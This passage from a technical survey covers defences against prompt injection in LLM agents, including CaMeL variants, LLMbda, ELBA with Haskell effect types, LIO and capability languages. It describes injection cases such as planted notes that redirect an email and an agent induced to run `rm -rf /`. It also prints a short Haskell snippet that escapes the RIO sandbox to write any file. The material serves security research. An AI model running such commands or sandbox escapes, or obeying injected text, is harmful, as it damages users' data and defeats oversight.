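messaging_agent("Send the text in 'summary' to Julie on Slack.",
                variables={"summary": summary})
```

The receiving agent's planner reads only the message. Its program can fetch the variables at run time, and they keep their labels, so a policy about who may read the applicants' data still applies in the second agent. The interpreter enforces the separation by refusing any call whose message depends on a tool's output.

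Peters-Gill and colleagues tested this on a version of AgentDojo with several agents, using five models and 949 attacks per model, with no policies on the data. On average, 12.9% of attacks succeeded without CaMeL, 0.2% with CaMeL in each agent, and none with Multi-CaMeL. Every attack that got past separate CaMeL agents was due to boundary laundering. On a benchmark of industrial maintenance tasks, running CaMeL in each agent lowered the success rate by an average of 21.6 percentage points, and Multi-CaMeL lowered it by a further 3.2.

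Multi-CaMeL extends CaMeL's interpreter, and Peters-Gill and colleagues acknowledge that it inherits the skipped-branch problem. The interpreter could therefore accept a message that depends on untrusted data if the dependency passes through an assignment that never ran. Multi-CaMeL does not retry failed programs, so it avoids the leak that retries can cause.

### LLMbda: labels on the conversation

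Garby and colleagues designed LLMbda so that the planner's code, the conversation with the model and the retry loop all run in one language under the same label rules. LLMbda is a form of the lambda calculus, a minimal language in which programs consist of functions. In the basic version, a label is a set that may contain U for untrusted and S for secret. An empty label means trusted and public. `l1 ⊑ l2` means that everything in `l1` is also in `l2`, and `l1 ⊔ l2` is their union.

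The conversation has a label as well, which combines the labels of all the messages the program has sent. A program can use four operations on it:

- `send` adds a message to the conversation.
- `recv` gets the model's reply, which LLMbda parses and runs as code. The shorthand `@` sends a prompt and receives the reply.
- `fork` runs an expression in a temporary copy of the conversation, then discards the copy and returns the result.
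- `clear` empties the conversation.

With these, a developer can write the dual-LLM pattern as a one-line function instead of building it into the system:

```
let quarantine = \prompt. fork (let _ = clear in @prompt) in

let notes  = find_file "meeting notes" in                              # label: U
let answer = quarantine ("What is Bob's email address? " + notes) in   # label: U
...
```

The quarantined model reads only the question and the notes. Its answer is untrusted, but the main conversation remains trusted because the notes never enter it. If the program had used `@` without `fork`, the conversation and every later reply would have become untrusted. This is the label creep described for FIDES, and here the programmer decides whether to accept it.

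### The rules that carry the labels

LLMbda also keeps a label called `pc`, short for program counter, for the decisions that led to the current point. Let `lc` be the label of the conversation. The main rules are:

```
send e        let n be the label of e
              requires pc ⊑ lc;   the new lc is lc ⊔ n
recv          requires pc ⊑ lc;   the reply runs with pc = lc
clear         requires pc ⊑ lc;   the new lc is pc
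fork e        runs e, then restores the old conversation and its label
f e           runs the body of f with pc = the label of f
assert l e    stops the run unless the label of e ⊑ l
```

The rule for function calls also handles conditionals, because LLMbda defines `if` in terms of functions. The result of whichever branch runs carries the label of the condition. Programs cannot reassign variables, so skipping a branch cannot leave a variable with an outdated label. The conversation is the only state that can change, and the requirement `pc ⊑ lc` protects it.

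For example, a program first tells the model to remember that x is false. If a secret is true, the program then tells the model that x is true. Finally, it asks for x. When the secret is true, LLMbda stops the program at the second message, because `pc` contains S and the conversation's label does not. Raising the label there would repeat CaMeL's flaw, since the label would stay public whenever the secret was false.

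The rule for `recv` covers code that the model writes. If the conversation contains untrusted text, any program in the reply starts with an untrusted `pc`, and everything it computes is untrusted. This holds for any reply, so the guarantee does not depend on the model resisting an injection.

These rules make an ordinary retry loop awkward. If an attempt reads untrusted data and fails, the error message makes the conversation untrusted, and the next program can no longer make a payment that requires trusted arguments. Randori, the agent that Garby and colleagues wrote in LLMbda, therefore tests and corrects its program against an invented bank account, where all data is trusted, then runs the final version once on the user's data. This also avoids repeating a payment when an attempt fails halfway.

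### What the theorem guarantees

Noninterference needs a careful definition here for two reasons. A model's replies are random, so the same program can end in different ways. A run may also never finish, because it loops forever or LLMbda stops it at a failed check.

Consider an observer at level *m*, who sees everything whose label is `⊑ m`. Two starting points are *m*-indistinguishable, written `~m`, if they differ only in parts this observer cannot see. For each starting point, let μ give the probability of every ending that the observer can tell apart. These probabilities may add up to less than 1, and the shortfall is the probability that the run never finishes. Garby and colleagues call two such distributions compatible if a third can cover both:

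```
μ ⌣ ν      if there is an ω with total at most 1 such that μ ≤ ω and ν ≤ ω

TIPNI(m):  if C0 ~m C1 and e0 ~m e1,
           then ⟦pc ⊢ C0, e0⟧m  ⌣  ⟦pc ⊢ C1, e1⟧m
```

Here C0 and C1 are conversations, e0 and e1 are programs with their data, and the double brackets stand for the distribution of endings at level *m*. The main theorem is that TIPNI (termination-insensitive probabilistic noninterference) holds for every *m* and every LLMbda program that does not use `endorse`, an operation for making deliberate exceptions.

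Hidden inputs may affect whether a run finishes, but they cannot otherwise change what the observer sees. Secrets cannot influence public results if *m* excludes S, and an attacker's text cannot influence trusted results if *m* excludes U.

Suppose a program asks the model to pick A or B, and the model picks A 60% of the time. If a secret is true and the model picked B, the program loops forever. Otherwise it returns the letter:

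| | Returns A | Returns B | Never finishes |
|---|---|---|---|
| Secret is false | 60% | 40% | 0% |
| Secret is true | 60% | 0% | 40% |

TIPNI allows this, because the first row covers both. It would forbid a program that always finished but returned A 60% of the time with one secret and 50% with the other, since covering both would need at least 60% for A and 50% for B, which add up to more than 100%. Garby and colleagues first tried a simpler definition that compares only the runs that finish, and found it wrong. That definition would reject the program in the table, where A's share of those runs rises from 60% to 100%.

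They also bound the remaining leak. The statistical distance between the two distributions is at most the average of their probabilities of never finishing, which are both 20% in the table. If both runs always finish, the distributions must be identical.

The proof uses a second way of running programs, in which any computation is skipped as soon as its label becomes invisible to the observer. The results of these runs don't depend on the hidden inputs, so their distribution is the same for both starting points. Each possible ending is at least as likely in these runs as in the real program, so this one distribution is an upper bound on both real ones.

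### What Lean verifies and what remains trusted

Garby and colleagues wrote LLMbda's rules, interpreter and proofs in Lean, a programming language and proof checker, and Lean checked the proofs. Another of their theorems connects the interpreter to the rules. It treats the model as an oracle, a function that supplies every reply. Running the interpreter with an oracle drawn at random according to the model's probabilities gives results with exactly the distribution that the rules prescribe. The theorems therefore describe the program that calls the model, whereas CaMeL's rules exist only as its Python code.

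For a larger program, a machine-checked proof can serve the purpose of Anderson's third requirement, but several things remain in the trusted base:

- Lean itself must be correct, both when it checks the proofs and when it runs the interpreter.
- The code that contacts the model over the network is outside the proofs. To Lean it is a function that returns some text.
- The theorem about the interpreter assumes that each reply depends only on the conversation so far and follows fixed probabilities. A service that let one user's conversation influence another's would break this assumption.
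- A developer has to label each data source correctly and put a check in each sensitive tool.

The treatment of tools leaves a larger gap. Garby and colleagues model them as functions inside LLMbda, and Randori's bank account is a value that the program passes along and returns at the end. A real email is sent immediately, even if the run later fails, but the theorem covers only how a run ends, not how long it takes. It also covers only one run at a time, so an operator who automatically restarted LLMbda after each failure would recreate the loop that leaks one bit per attempt in CaMeL.

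### Endorsement

A useful agent sometimes has to act on untrusted data. LLMbda's `endorse` marks such data as trusted and makes that decision visible in the program. In Garby and colleagues' example, an agent replies to an email and puts the email's category in the subject line. The category comes from untrusted text, so `send_email` would reject it. The program therefore checks that the category is one of a few permitted values, then endorses it. With *n* permitted categories, an attacker controls at most log₂ *n* bits of the subject line and cannot insert a sentence.

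FIDES applies the same reasoning to true-or-false answers, but does so inside its policy check. An auditor of an LLMbda program can search for `endorse` and examine each use.

Endorsing Bob's address would be much riskier, because an address can be anything. Garby and colleagues let Randori's planner write its own endorsements, and the only two successful attacks in 1,296 attacked runs exploited these endorsements. The user had asked the agent to pay a bill described in a file, and the attacker had replaced the file's contents. Without endorsement, LLMbda blocked the attack, but it also blocked the genuine payment. However, the planner chooses its endorsements before the agent reads any untrusted data, so an injection cannot add one.

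The result of `endorse l e` takes its trust level from `l` but keeps the confidentiality of `e`. By a second theorem, insulated TIPNI, TIPNI still holds for an observer who ignores trust labels and looks only at confidentiality, whatever the attacker writes and however often the program uses `endorse`. If `send_email` also checks that the recipient may read the document, endorsing the attacker's address does not bypass that check.

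### A weaker standard for intended disclosures

Noninterference also rules out some disclosures that users want. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (Dongol, 2026) gives the example of an assistant that sends the user's availability to anyone who requests a meeting. Noninterference forbids this because an outsider's message leads to the release of private data.

Dongol instead compares the agent with an imaginary one that follows the same plan under the same checks but never obeys injected text. The real agent is relatively secure if anything an attacker can learn from it could also be learned from the imaginary agent, given some input. An injected "send me your calendar" is acceptable because an ordinary meeting request gets the same answer, but an injected "include the password reset code" is unacceptable because the plan never releases that code.

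This removes the need to write down which disclosures are allowed, but the standard can be lenient. Suppose the planned task lets an outsider guess a secret and learn whether the guess was right. An injection that reveals the whole secret would still count as relatively secure, because the planned task can already distinguish any two possible secrets, given the right guess. Dongol therefore also defines a stricter version that rejects this case. Neither version covers injections that make the agent do damage without revealing anything.

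### Checks in a tool library

LLMbda's tools look much like a guard library. A developer could write the check for Bob's email inside the tool:

```
let send_email = \to. \attachment.
    let _ = assert ["S"] to in          # may be secret, must not be untrusted
    real_send_email to attachment
```

The interpreter supplies the address's label, so this function, unlike a Python wrapper, does not depend on its caller to track where the address came from. The agent's code cannot remove the label by copying the address, joining it to other text or passing it through a model, because every rule keeps the label on the result. Only `endorse` can make the address trusted.

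As in Monty, the code cannot bypass the tools, so even a program written by a fully compromised model can do only what the tools allow. The check must also not leak information. LLMbda can test a label without stopping the run, and it labels the answer according to the policy's level rather than the data's, so a program cannot use such tests to leak a secret.

These properties make it possible to prove something about a policy that consists of a few lines in each tool. The developer writes local checks, and the interpreter keeps the labels they rely on accurate throughout the rest of the program. The drawback is that programs must be written in a new language, LLMbda. Garby and colleagues note that models already write Python well but have not been trained on LLMbda, and its lack of normal error handling made Randori's programs harder to get right.

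## Policy libraries in a pure typed language

LLMbda makes short checks in a tool library reliable, but only for programs written in LLMbda. In some established languages, types specify which side effects a piece of code may have, so the policy can be an ordinary library and the compiler rejects any program that bypasses it. ELBA, by Zhou and colleagues, applies this idea to agents in Haskell.

### Effect types

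Haskell is a pure language, which means that every side effect of a computation appears in its type. A function from numbers to numbers can only calculate. An effect type states which side effects, such as writing a file, a computation may have, and Haskell's most general one is `IO`:

```haskell
factorial :: Int -> Int              -- calculates and does nothing else
readFile  :: String -> IO String     -- may act on the outside world
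system    :: String -> IO ExitCode   -- runs a shell command
```

The `::` means "has type", and the type after the last arrow is the result. Any program that runs `system` also has an `IO` type, even if the call is nested deep inside other functions.

Zhou and colleagues illustrate this with a public calculator. A model writes a program for each visitor's question, and the program must have type `Int`. If a visitor asks the model to delete the server's files and then compute the factorial of 5, the model may write a program that runs `rm -rf /` before the calculation. That program has type `IO Int`, so the compiler rejects it without needing a list of forbidden commands. The same rule stops the agent that opened its own network connection in Python, because Haskell's functions for opening connections also have `IO` types.

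*ETAS* (2026) points out that most agent frameworks connect agents through callbacks and tool registries, whose parameter and return types do not describe what the agents do, so a type checker cannot check it. It proposes a new language with effect types for agents, but a Haskell developer needs only a library.

### A narrower effect with a hidden constructor

A program of type `Int` cannot do anything useful in the world, and one of type `IO` can do everything. A library can define an effect type in between. Terei, Mazières and colleagues, in *Safe Haskell*, give an example called RIO, for "restricted IO". A slightly adapted version looks like this:

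```haskell
module RIO (RIO, runRIO, rioReadFile) where

newtype RIO a = UnsafeRIO (IO a)

runRIO :: RIO a -> IO a
runRIO (UnsafeRIO action) = action

rioReadFile :: FilePath -> RIO String
rioReadFile file = UnsafeRIO (do
    ok <- pathOK file                          -- the policy
    if ok then readFile file else return "")
```

The constructor `UnsafeRIO` wraps an `IO` computation to make an `RIO` computation. The top line lists the module's exports and omits `UnsafeRIO`, so `RIO` is an abstract type, which other modules can use only through the exported functions. Agent code can call `rioReadFile` and chain `RIO` steps (the definitions for chaining are left out here), but it cannot wrap a call to `system`. The exported `runRIO` only removes the wrapper, so that the application can run the finished program.

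`rioReadFile` is a guard around a tool, like the Python wrapper for `send_email`, but agent code cannot bypass it. The original `readFile` is still available, but a program that runs it has the wrong type.

### Safe Haskell

All this assumes that code cannot lie about its type or get hold of a hidden constructor. Ordinary Haskell allows both. Terei and colleagues list four ways for a malicious module to escape from RIO:

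- The function `unsafePerformIO` has type `IO a -> a`. It runs any action and presents the result as a pure value.
- Haskell can import functions written in C, and the programmer declares their types. The compiler cannot check whether a C function declared as pure really is.
- Haskell identifies types at run time through a class called `Typeable`. A handwritten entry for `RIO` can claim that it is the same type as `IO`, and a cast then converts one into the other.
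- Template Haskell, which generates code during compilation, can reach constructors that a module does not export.

Safe Haskell blocks all four. It has been part of GHC, the main Haskell compiler, since version 7.2. A module compiled in Safe mode cannot use the dangerous features and can import only trusted modules. A trusted module is either Safe itself or marked Trustworthy, which means its author promises that it uses unsafe features internally but offers a safe interface. Haskell's fast byte strings need the Trustworthy mark because they access memory directly.

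Any author can write "Trustworthy" at the top of a module. The *Safe Haskell* chapter of GHC's user guide therefore recommends an option that accepts the mark only in packages the person compiling has chosen to trust. The option is off by default.

Terei and colleagues designed Safe Haskell to make types reliable and to leave policy to libraries like RIO. A Safe program can therefore still delete all of a user's files if its type includes `IO`. The team used Safe Haskell to build a website that ran Haskell code from unknown visitors, and its policy, which allowed no input or output, took six lines.

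Stinner's restricted Python became too limited for real programs, but Haskell's safe subset is large. In 2012 Terei and colleagues compiled every package on Hackage, Haskell's public archive, and 83% met the restrictions on language features. Only 27% of modules counted as safe once GHC also checked their imports, partly because several standard modules mixed safe and unsafe functions, which made everything that imported them unsafe.

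### From a prompt to a checked program

ELBA adds one function to Haskell:

```haskell
agent :: Defs -> Prompt -> t
```

`Defs` lists the types and functions the model may use, `Prompt` describes the task, and `t` is whatever type the surrounding program expects. When the application reaches an `agent` call, ELBA does the following:

1. It sends the model the prompt, the definitions and the expected type.
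2. It type-checks the Haskell expression that the model returns. If the check fails, it sends the compiler's error message back and the model tries again.
3. It runs the accepted program in a Haskell interpreter and returns the result to the application.

The developer often doesn't need to write the expected type. If the application sorts the results of several `agent` calls with a function that compares dates, Haskell infers that each call must return a date. ELBA passes the inferred type on, so even a vague prompt like "parse this" becomes clear.

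A rejected program has no effect. *LACUNA* (Zhao, Xu and colleagues, 2026), which presents a similar design for Scala, shows why this matters. In its example, an application holds a balance of 100 and asks the model for code that subtracts 50 and returns the new balance as a whole number. The model's code subtracts 50 but returns a sentence. An untyped language would change the balance before the error appeared, and a second attempt might subtract another 50. The Scala compiler rejects the whole snippet, so the balance is still 100 when the model tries again.

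ELBA's retries also avoid the leak in CaMeL's retry loop, because a type error arises before the program has read anything.

### Only entries from DBLP

The bibliography agent must write only entries fetched from DBLP, but it should be free to sort and filter them. Zhou and colleagues define an effect type, `BibIO`, and an abstract type, `Trusted`. In simplified form, the library offers:

```haskell
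dblpSearch      :: String -> BibIO [DOI]
dblpFetchBib    :: DOI -> BibIO (Trusted Bib)
appendToBibFile :: Trusted Bib -> BibIO ()
```

A DOI is a permanent identifier for a publication, and `()` means that a step returns nothing useful. The application asks the agent for a program of type `BibIO ()`. The model might write:

```haskell
do dois    <- dblpSearch "differential privacy"
   entries <- mapM dblpFetchBib dois              -- fetch each entry
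   mapM_ appendToBibFile (sortOn year entries)    -- write them, oldest first
```

This passes the check, assuming that the library also lets programs read an entry's year. If the model instead makes up an entry, it can't save it with `writeFile`, because `BibIO` limits which operations the agent can use, and a step of type `IO ()` does not fit into a `BibIO` program. Passing the text to `appendToBibFile` also fails to compile, because that function requires a `Trusted Bib`, which only `dblpFetchBib` can produce.

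Zhou and colleagues tested this on 100 tasks, each asking for citations on a computer science topic. They compared ELBA with an ordinary tool-calling agent with web search, running both on Claude Sonnet 5. A citation counted as hallucinated if its authors, year or DOI were wrong. ELBA's agent hallucinated none of its 925 citations, and the other agent hallucinated 19 of 1,002.

The types guarantee the count of zero, provided that DBLP's data is right. However, the comparison doesn't isolate the effect of the types, because the other agent composed its citations from search results and memory. A combined fetch-and-write tool would also have prevented made-up entries, though without the sorting and filtering. The count also didn't measure relevance. An ELBA agent can add a genuine paper on the wrong subject, and a program that writes nothing also has type `BibIO ()`.

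### Bob's address as a type

The same technique can protect Bob's email. A mail library could offer these functions:

```haskell
lookUpContact :: Name -> MailIO (Trusted Address)
askUser       :: Address -> MailIO (Maybe (Trusted Address))
sendEmail     :: Trusted Address -> Document -> MailIO ()
```

A program that takes the address from the meeting notes and passes it directly to `sendEmail` fails the type check before the agent opens the notes. The model learns from the error message that it needs a `Trusted Address`, so it can rewrite the program to call `askUser`, which returns one only if the user approves. This design doesn't label values at run time.

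The types capture only the distinctions the library's author thought of. If the program passes a name from the notes to `lookUpContact`, a planted note can replace Bob with Ana, and the lookup then returns a properly trusted address for the wrong person.

### Sub-agents under the same policy

One `agent` call produces one complete program, but many tasks require the agent to look at a result before deciding what to do next. In ELBA, the generated program can itself call `agent`. Zhou and colleagues' bibliography agent might run a search, fetch the first hit, and put it in the prompt of a sub-agent that decides whether to refine the search or start writing. Repeating this gives the usual agent loop.

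The call to the sub-agent sits inside a `BibIO` program, so Haskell infers that the sub-agent's program must also have type `BibIO ()`. The parent can tighten this limit by asking for a plain `String`, which rules out all of the library's actions. It cannot loosen the limit, because a sub-agent's program of type `IO ()` would not type-check inside the parent's program.

Unlike CaMeL's planner, a sub-agent in ELBA may read a hostile search result and write its next program under the attacker's influence. The types still confine that program to the three `BibIO` operations, but the attacker can choose among them.

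ELBA's sub-agents receive only a task description and one string of data. In LACUNA, a nested call also receives the surrounding source code, including the variables and comments that the outer snippet has added. This helps the model understand its part of the task, but it also exposes the model to any sentence planted in those comments.

### File access through paths

The bibliography library restricts what a program may write. For general file access, Zhou and colleagues built their own `RIO`, which uses capabilities instead of testing file names. Its `readRIO` and `writeRIO` functions require a `Path`, the directory capability from the earlier Haskell example.

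The application starts a program with `evalRIO`, which gives it a `Path` for one root directory. The program derives others with the operator `//`:

```haskell
backUpNotes :: Path -> RIO ()
backUpNotes folder = do
    text <- readRIO (folder // "notes.txt")
    writeRIO (folder // "backup.txt") text
```

The types guarantee that every `Path` comes from the one the application granted, but they don't show where `folder // "../secrets"` leads or whether `notes.txt` is a symbolic link to a file elsewhere. The `//` operator therefore resolves each path at run time, follows any links, and rejects any result outside the original directory. A program that passes the type check can still fail this run-time check.

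Since a `Path` is an ordinary value, a program can pass it on. A parent agent could ask a sub-agent for a function of type `Path -> RIO ()` and call it with a `Path` for a single subfolder. Zhou and colleagues suggest that capabilities could also cover resources other than folders, such as all the files on one branch of a code repository.

### LIO: one label for everything in view

The developer of a type like `Trusted` has to decide in advance which origins matter. Information-flow control handles origins and readers more generally, and Haskell already had a library for it, LIO, which ELBA uses without modification. Stefan, Russo and colleagues describe LIO in *Flexible Dynamic Information Flow Control in the Presence of Exceptions*.

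CaMeL's interpreter can label every value because it creates every value. A library cannot do this without changing Haskell's runtime. LIO instead keeps one current label that covers everything the program can see at that moment. In the notation used for LLMbda, with `l1 ⊑ l2` now read as "data labelled l1 may flow to a place labelled l2", the main rules are:

```
read data labelled l         the current label becomes  current ⊔ l
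write to a place labelled l  allowed only if  current ⊑ l
```

A program that starts with the label Public can read a Secret file, but its current label then becomes Secret and it can no longer write anywhere public. Labels in ELBA also record who influenced the data. In one of Zhou and colleagues' examples, a program fetches a page from phony.com and tries to write the contents to the user. The fetch adds phony.com to the current label's sources, and LIO stops the write because writing to the user requires a more trustworthy source.

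Haskell's types only ensure that agent code has LIO's own effect type and therefore cannot use plain `IO`. LIO's functions compare the labels while the program runs.

LIO also has an abstract type, `Labeled`, for individual values, because a single label would spread distrust as quickly as FIDES's label on a whole conversation. A program can store a `Labeled` value, pass it on and inspect its label without affecting the current label. It must call `unlabel` to see the contents, and that call raises the current label.

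This solves the skipped-branch problem that Garby and colleagues found in CaMeL. In LIO the bank balance from their example would be a `Labeled` value, and an `if` needs an ordinary true or false. The program has to unlabel the balance before it can branch, which makes the current label Secret from then on. LIO would therefore refuse the email to the outsider whichever branch runs.

### The dual-LLM pattern with toLabeled

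A program often needs to work on sensitive data for a moment without carrying the label for the rest of its run. The function `toLabeled` takes a label `l` and a computation, and proceeds as follows:

1. It checks that the current label may flow to `l`.
2. It runs the computation, which may raise the current label by reading data.
3. It checks that the raised label still may flow to `l`.
4. It restores the old current label and returns the result as a `Labeled` value with label `l`.

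The program has to choose `l` before the computation starts. An early version of LIO instead used whatever label the computation ended with. Under that rule, if programs could still inspect labels without restriction, a program could read a secret bit inside the computation, raise the label to Top Secret only if the bit was true, and then learn the bit by inspecting the label from outside.

Zhou and colleagues use `toLabeled` to express the dual-LLM pattern. In outline, the agent for Bob's email could write:

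```haskell
do notes    <- findFile "meeting notes"             -- a Labeled value
   address  <- toLabeled fromNotes (do
                   text <- unlabel notes
                   subagent "What is Bob's email address?" text)
   ...
   sendEmail address document
```

The sub-agent reads the notes, and the outer agent receives an address that it can pass on but has not seen. The outer agent's label doesn't change. `sendEmail` belongs to the trusted library, so it can read the address and apply a policy like CaMeL's, such as checking whether the recipient is already allowed to read the document.

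The sub-agent can keep its tools, unlike the quarantined model in Willison's pattern, because LIO checks the sub-agent's current label at each call. After reading the notes, it could still look something up, but LIO would block an action that requires trusted input. ELBA can therefore give its sub-agents more to do. With policies enabled, it completed roughly twice as many of AgentDojo's Slack tasks as CaMeL.

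LIO can also limit what a computation may read. Each program has a clearance, which is an upper limit on its current label. The program can lower its clearance but not raise it. Stefan and colleagues wrote a conference reviewing system in which a malicious component could read a rival's paper inside `toLabeled` and leak the paper's contents by choosing whether to loop forever. If the system sets the clearance to what the current user may read, `unlabel` fails on the rival's paper, so the component can't read the contents or leak them.

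### Programs that stop halfway

Labels often depend on facts known only at run time, such as who has logged in, so LIO may still stop a program that has passed the type check. ELBA retries after type errors but not after run-time errors, which avoids resending an email but leaves the task unfinished.

The program can catch and handle such a refusal, because LIO reports violations as exceptions. A refusal inside `toLabeled` could reveal something about the data there, so LIO does not let exceptions escape from the block.

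Stefan and colleagues argue that checking at run time also has an advantage. A purely static checker rejects a program if any line breaks the rules, even a line that never runs, while LIO stops a run only when it is about to break them. *HLIO* (Buiras, Russo and Vytiniotis, 2015) combines static and run-time checking, letting programmers choose which checks to defer until the program runs.

LIO's security guarantees don't cover leaks through timing or through programs that never finish. `toLabeled` waits for its computation to finish, so the timing of the program's next action can reveal how long the computation took. A sub-agent's running time could vary a good deal with what it reads. The *LIO.Concurrent* documentation on Hackage presents an alternative, `lFork`, which starts the computation in a separate thread and returns at once. The program's label then rises only if the program waits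 for the result. Source code comments in one version on Hackage strongly recommend `lFork` over `toLabeled`.

### The soundness theorem

Zhou and colleagues prove that adding agents to a typed language does not weaken what its types guarantee. Let L be the host language together with its policy libraries. A trace is the sequence of tool calls with observable side effects that one run makes, and `traces(e)` is the set of traces that program `e` can produce. A condition P on such sets is a property of type `t` if:

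```
for every program e in L:    e has type t   implies   P(traces(e))
```

For `BibIO ()`, P could be "every write contains only data from DBLP". Because P applies to a whole set of traces, it can also express policies that compare runs. Schneider showed that a monitor that watches one run at a time cannot enforce such policies.

Under the theorem, every property of a type in L still holds for that type when L is extended with the `agent` function.

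To prove it, take any program `e` of type `t` that contains agent calls. It is enough to find a program in plain L with the same type and the same traces, because P holds for every program of that type in L. Zhou and colleagues construct it by replacing each agent call with an ordinary function, here called `a`, that queries the model itself:

```
a(0,   defs, prompt)  =  Nothing
a(n+1, defs, prompt)  =  the result of the model's program, with each agent
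                         call in it replaced by a(m, ...) where m ≤ n,
                         if that program type-checks
                      =  Nothing otherwise
```

The model's program may contain agent calls that generate programs with further agent calls, so every call has a depth limit. At depth 0, both the agent call and its replacement return `Nothing`. If they behave alike at every depth up to n, they also behave alike at n+1, because all calls in the generated program have depth n or less. Replacing every agent call therefore leaves the traces unchanged.

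The proof treats the model as an arbitrary function from prompts to programs. It assumes nothing about the model's honesty or skill, so the theorem holds even if an attacker completely controls the model's answers.

The traces record tool calls but not requests to the model. An `agent` call may have type `Int`, which normally rules out every side effect, yet it sends its prompt to whichever company runs the model. A program that LIO would stop from posting a secret online could still put it in a sub-agent's prompt. If the policy is meant to protect data from that company too, the developer needs a locally run model or a version of `agent` that checks labels before it sends anything.

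### One language for the whole application

The theorem covers only code written in the host language, so the tools, the retry logic and the rest of the application should all be in Haskell. Zhou and colleagues stress this requirement, but their AgentDojo tests met it only partly because the benchmark's tools are in Python and ELBA called them through a separate process. Haskell's types controlled which requests reached that process, but the Python code running there remained trusted.

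Many real applications would have the same boundary, because most established agent frameworks are for Python and JavaScript. A developer can keep it narrow by giving each Python tool one Haskell function with a precise type. Another Python component that called the same tools directly would bypass the policy.

### Trust in the compiler

LACUNA's trusted base consists of the compiler, the runtime and the program that issues the agent call, and ELBA's is much the same. A production compiler is far too large for the complete analysis that Anderson required. Bugs in its type checker also become more serious when security depends on it. In a discussion reproduced in *Safe Haskell?* (Eisenberg, 2021), Bertram Felgenhauer observed that such bugs usually affect only code that people shouldn't write anyway, but Safe Haskell turns them into potential security problems. An attacker who influences a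 model can ask it for such code.

Safe mode also depends on GHC's developers remembering to forbid each new unsafe feature. According to Hécate's *Deprecating Safe Haskell, or heavily investing in it?* (2022), `DerivingVia`, which can break module boundaries, was not on the list of forbidden features until May 2021. Pysandbox's list of dangerous attributes had the same weakness.

Hécate wanted the Haskell community either to invest heavily in Safe Haskell or to remove it and keep only a mechanism for restricting `IO`. Eisenberg had started to write a proposal to remove it, then decided that it needed renovation as part of a larger security effort. The current GHC guide still documents Safe Haskell, so it has not been retired as Java's Security Manager was, but an agent's security would depend on a feature with doubtful support.

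Compiling hostile code can itself be dangerous, because GHC has options that run other programs during compilation. Its guide therefore recommends compiling untrusted source code in a sandbox. ELBA reduces this risk by asking the model for a single expression. Compiler options, C imports and handwritten `Typeable` entries belong outside expressions, so the model cannot include them.

Types do not limit time or memory either. A program of type `Int` can loop forever, and Terei and colleagues knew of no remedy except the operating system's limits on processes.

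### Trust in the library and its policy

A policy library is itself trusted code. Stefan and colleagues checked a large part of LIO's theory with the proof assistant Coq, and ELBA benefits from that work by reusing LIO. A library like `BibIO`, written for one application, normally has no proof, so somebody must carefully read its few short functions.

A policy library's list of exports needs as much care as its functions. In a blog post, ezyang (2012) describes an HTML library with an internal module that exports the constructor for escaped text (text made safe to show on a web page). GHC infers that the module is safe because it uses no dangerous feature. Untrusted code can then import the constructor, label a malicious script as escaped text, and pass it to an application that relies on the type. To prevent this, the library's author has to mark the module Unsafe by hand.

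The standard RIO example contains a mistake of this kind. Both Terei and colleagues' paper and the current GHC guide define `runRIO` as a named field of the wrapper:

```haskell
newtype RIO a = UnsafeRIO { runRIO :: IO a }
```

Their modules hide `UnsafeRIO` but export `runRIO`. In Haskell, code that can see a field's name can make a copy of a value with that field changed, even if the constructor is hidden. An untrusted program can therefore start with a harmless `RIO` value and replace its contents:

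```haskell
escape :: RIO ()
escape = (return ()) { runRIO = writeFile "/any/file" "anything" }
```

This code uses no unsafe feature and has exactly the type the application requires, but it never calls `pathOK`. Defining `runRIO` as a separate function, as in the adapted version above, prevents this bypass.

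## Capability languages

In an object-capability language, every file, network connection and tool is an object, and a program can use an object only if it holds a reference to it. Within one Haskell library, ELBA's `Path` already works this way for directories. A capability language applies this rule to everything, so agent code can access only what the application passes to it.

### Access only through references

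Miller and Shapiro, in *Paradigm Regained*, compare two Unix commands that copy a file:

```
cp foo.txt bar.txt
cat < foo.txt > bar.txt
```

The first command gives `cp` two file names. Because the user might name any file, `cp` needs all of the user's access. In the second command, the shell opens both files and passes them to `cat`. Unix still gives `cat` all of the user's access, but `cat` needs only the two open files for this job. An object-capability language supports only the second style.

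Code can get a reference in three ways. Its creator can supply one, it can create a new object itself, or another object can pass it one in a message. Miller and Shapiro summarize this as "only connectivity begets connectivity". Suppose a planning component holds references to a mailer and a document reader. It can pass the mailer reference to the document reader. If it doesn't, and no other component with a reference to the mailer can reach the document reader, the document reader can never send email.

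Many object-oriented languages come close to this rule but leave ways around it. C++ lets a program turn a number into a pointer. Java has static variables, through which two objects can communicate even if neither holds a reference to the other. CPython is further from following the rule, as the escapes from pysandbox showed.

Controlling references does not fully control information. Miller and Shapiro distinguish permission, which is direct access to an object, from authority, which also covers what a program can achieve through others. A component with no reference to a file can still learn its contents if another component reads the file and passes on a copy.

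### E

E is a language that follows the object-capability model. Miller (2006), in *Robust Composition*, shows how an E program can divide access by creating several objects that share something private. His example is a counter with one object that can only count up and another that can only count down. A mailbox could work the same way:

```
def makeMailbox(server) {
    def reader { to latest()      { return server.fetch() } }
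    def toBob  { to send(message) { server.deliver("bob@acme.example", message) } }
    return [reader, toBob]
}
```

Code that receives only `toBob` can write to Bob and nobody else. It cannot read the inbox or get `server` out of the object.

E detects most mistakes only when the program runs. For example, if code calls `reader.send(...)` and `reader` has no `send` method, E detects the error when it executes the call. A variable can also have a guard, which checks each value before assignment. The guard `Data` accepts only values that carry information and give no access to anything.

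### What Joe-E takes out of Java

Mettler, Wagner and Close (2010) turned Java into an object-capability language, Joe-E, by removing features. A Joe-E program is ordinary Java that also passes a verifier, which checks one source file at a time without modifying it. The standard Java compiler and JVM then compile and run the program.

| Joe-E forbids | With this feature, code could |
|---|---|
| Native methods, written in a language such as C | Do anything, including forge references |
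| Library functions that reach the outside world without a capability | Open any file by name |
| Static fields whose contents can change | Pass data and references through global variables |
| Reflection that ignores `private` | Take references out of other objects |
| Exceptions that can hold a capability | Leak a reference to a caller that should not have it |
| `finalize` methods, `finally` blocks and catching serious errors | Use objects that are half-built or in an inconsistent state |

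The restrictions on library functions and static fields remove ambient authority, the access that code has merely because it is running. In ordinary Java, any code can create a `File` object from a path and then read or delete that file. In Joe-E, code can do this only if it has received an object for the file or for a directory above it.

This also makes stack inspection unnecessary. A Joe-E clock object, for example, could keep its own reference to the time zone file, so its callers would not need access to it.

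The hard part is taming, Mettler and colleagues' term for going through Java's standard library and deciding which methods are safe. Java's `getParentFile` returns the directory above a file, so a program with one file could climb to the root and reach everything. The danger in the constructor `new File(dir, name)` is less obvious. It normally finds a file inside a given directory, but if `dir` is null, Java treats `name` as a full path. Joe-E blocks the constructor and offers a wrapper that first checks for null.

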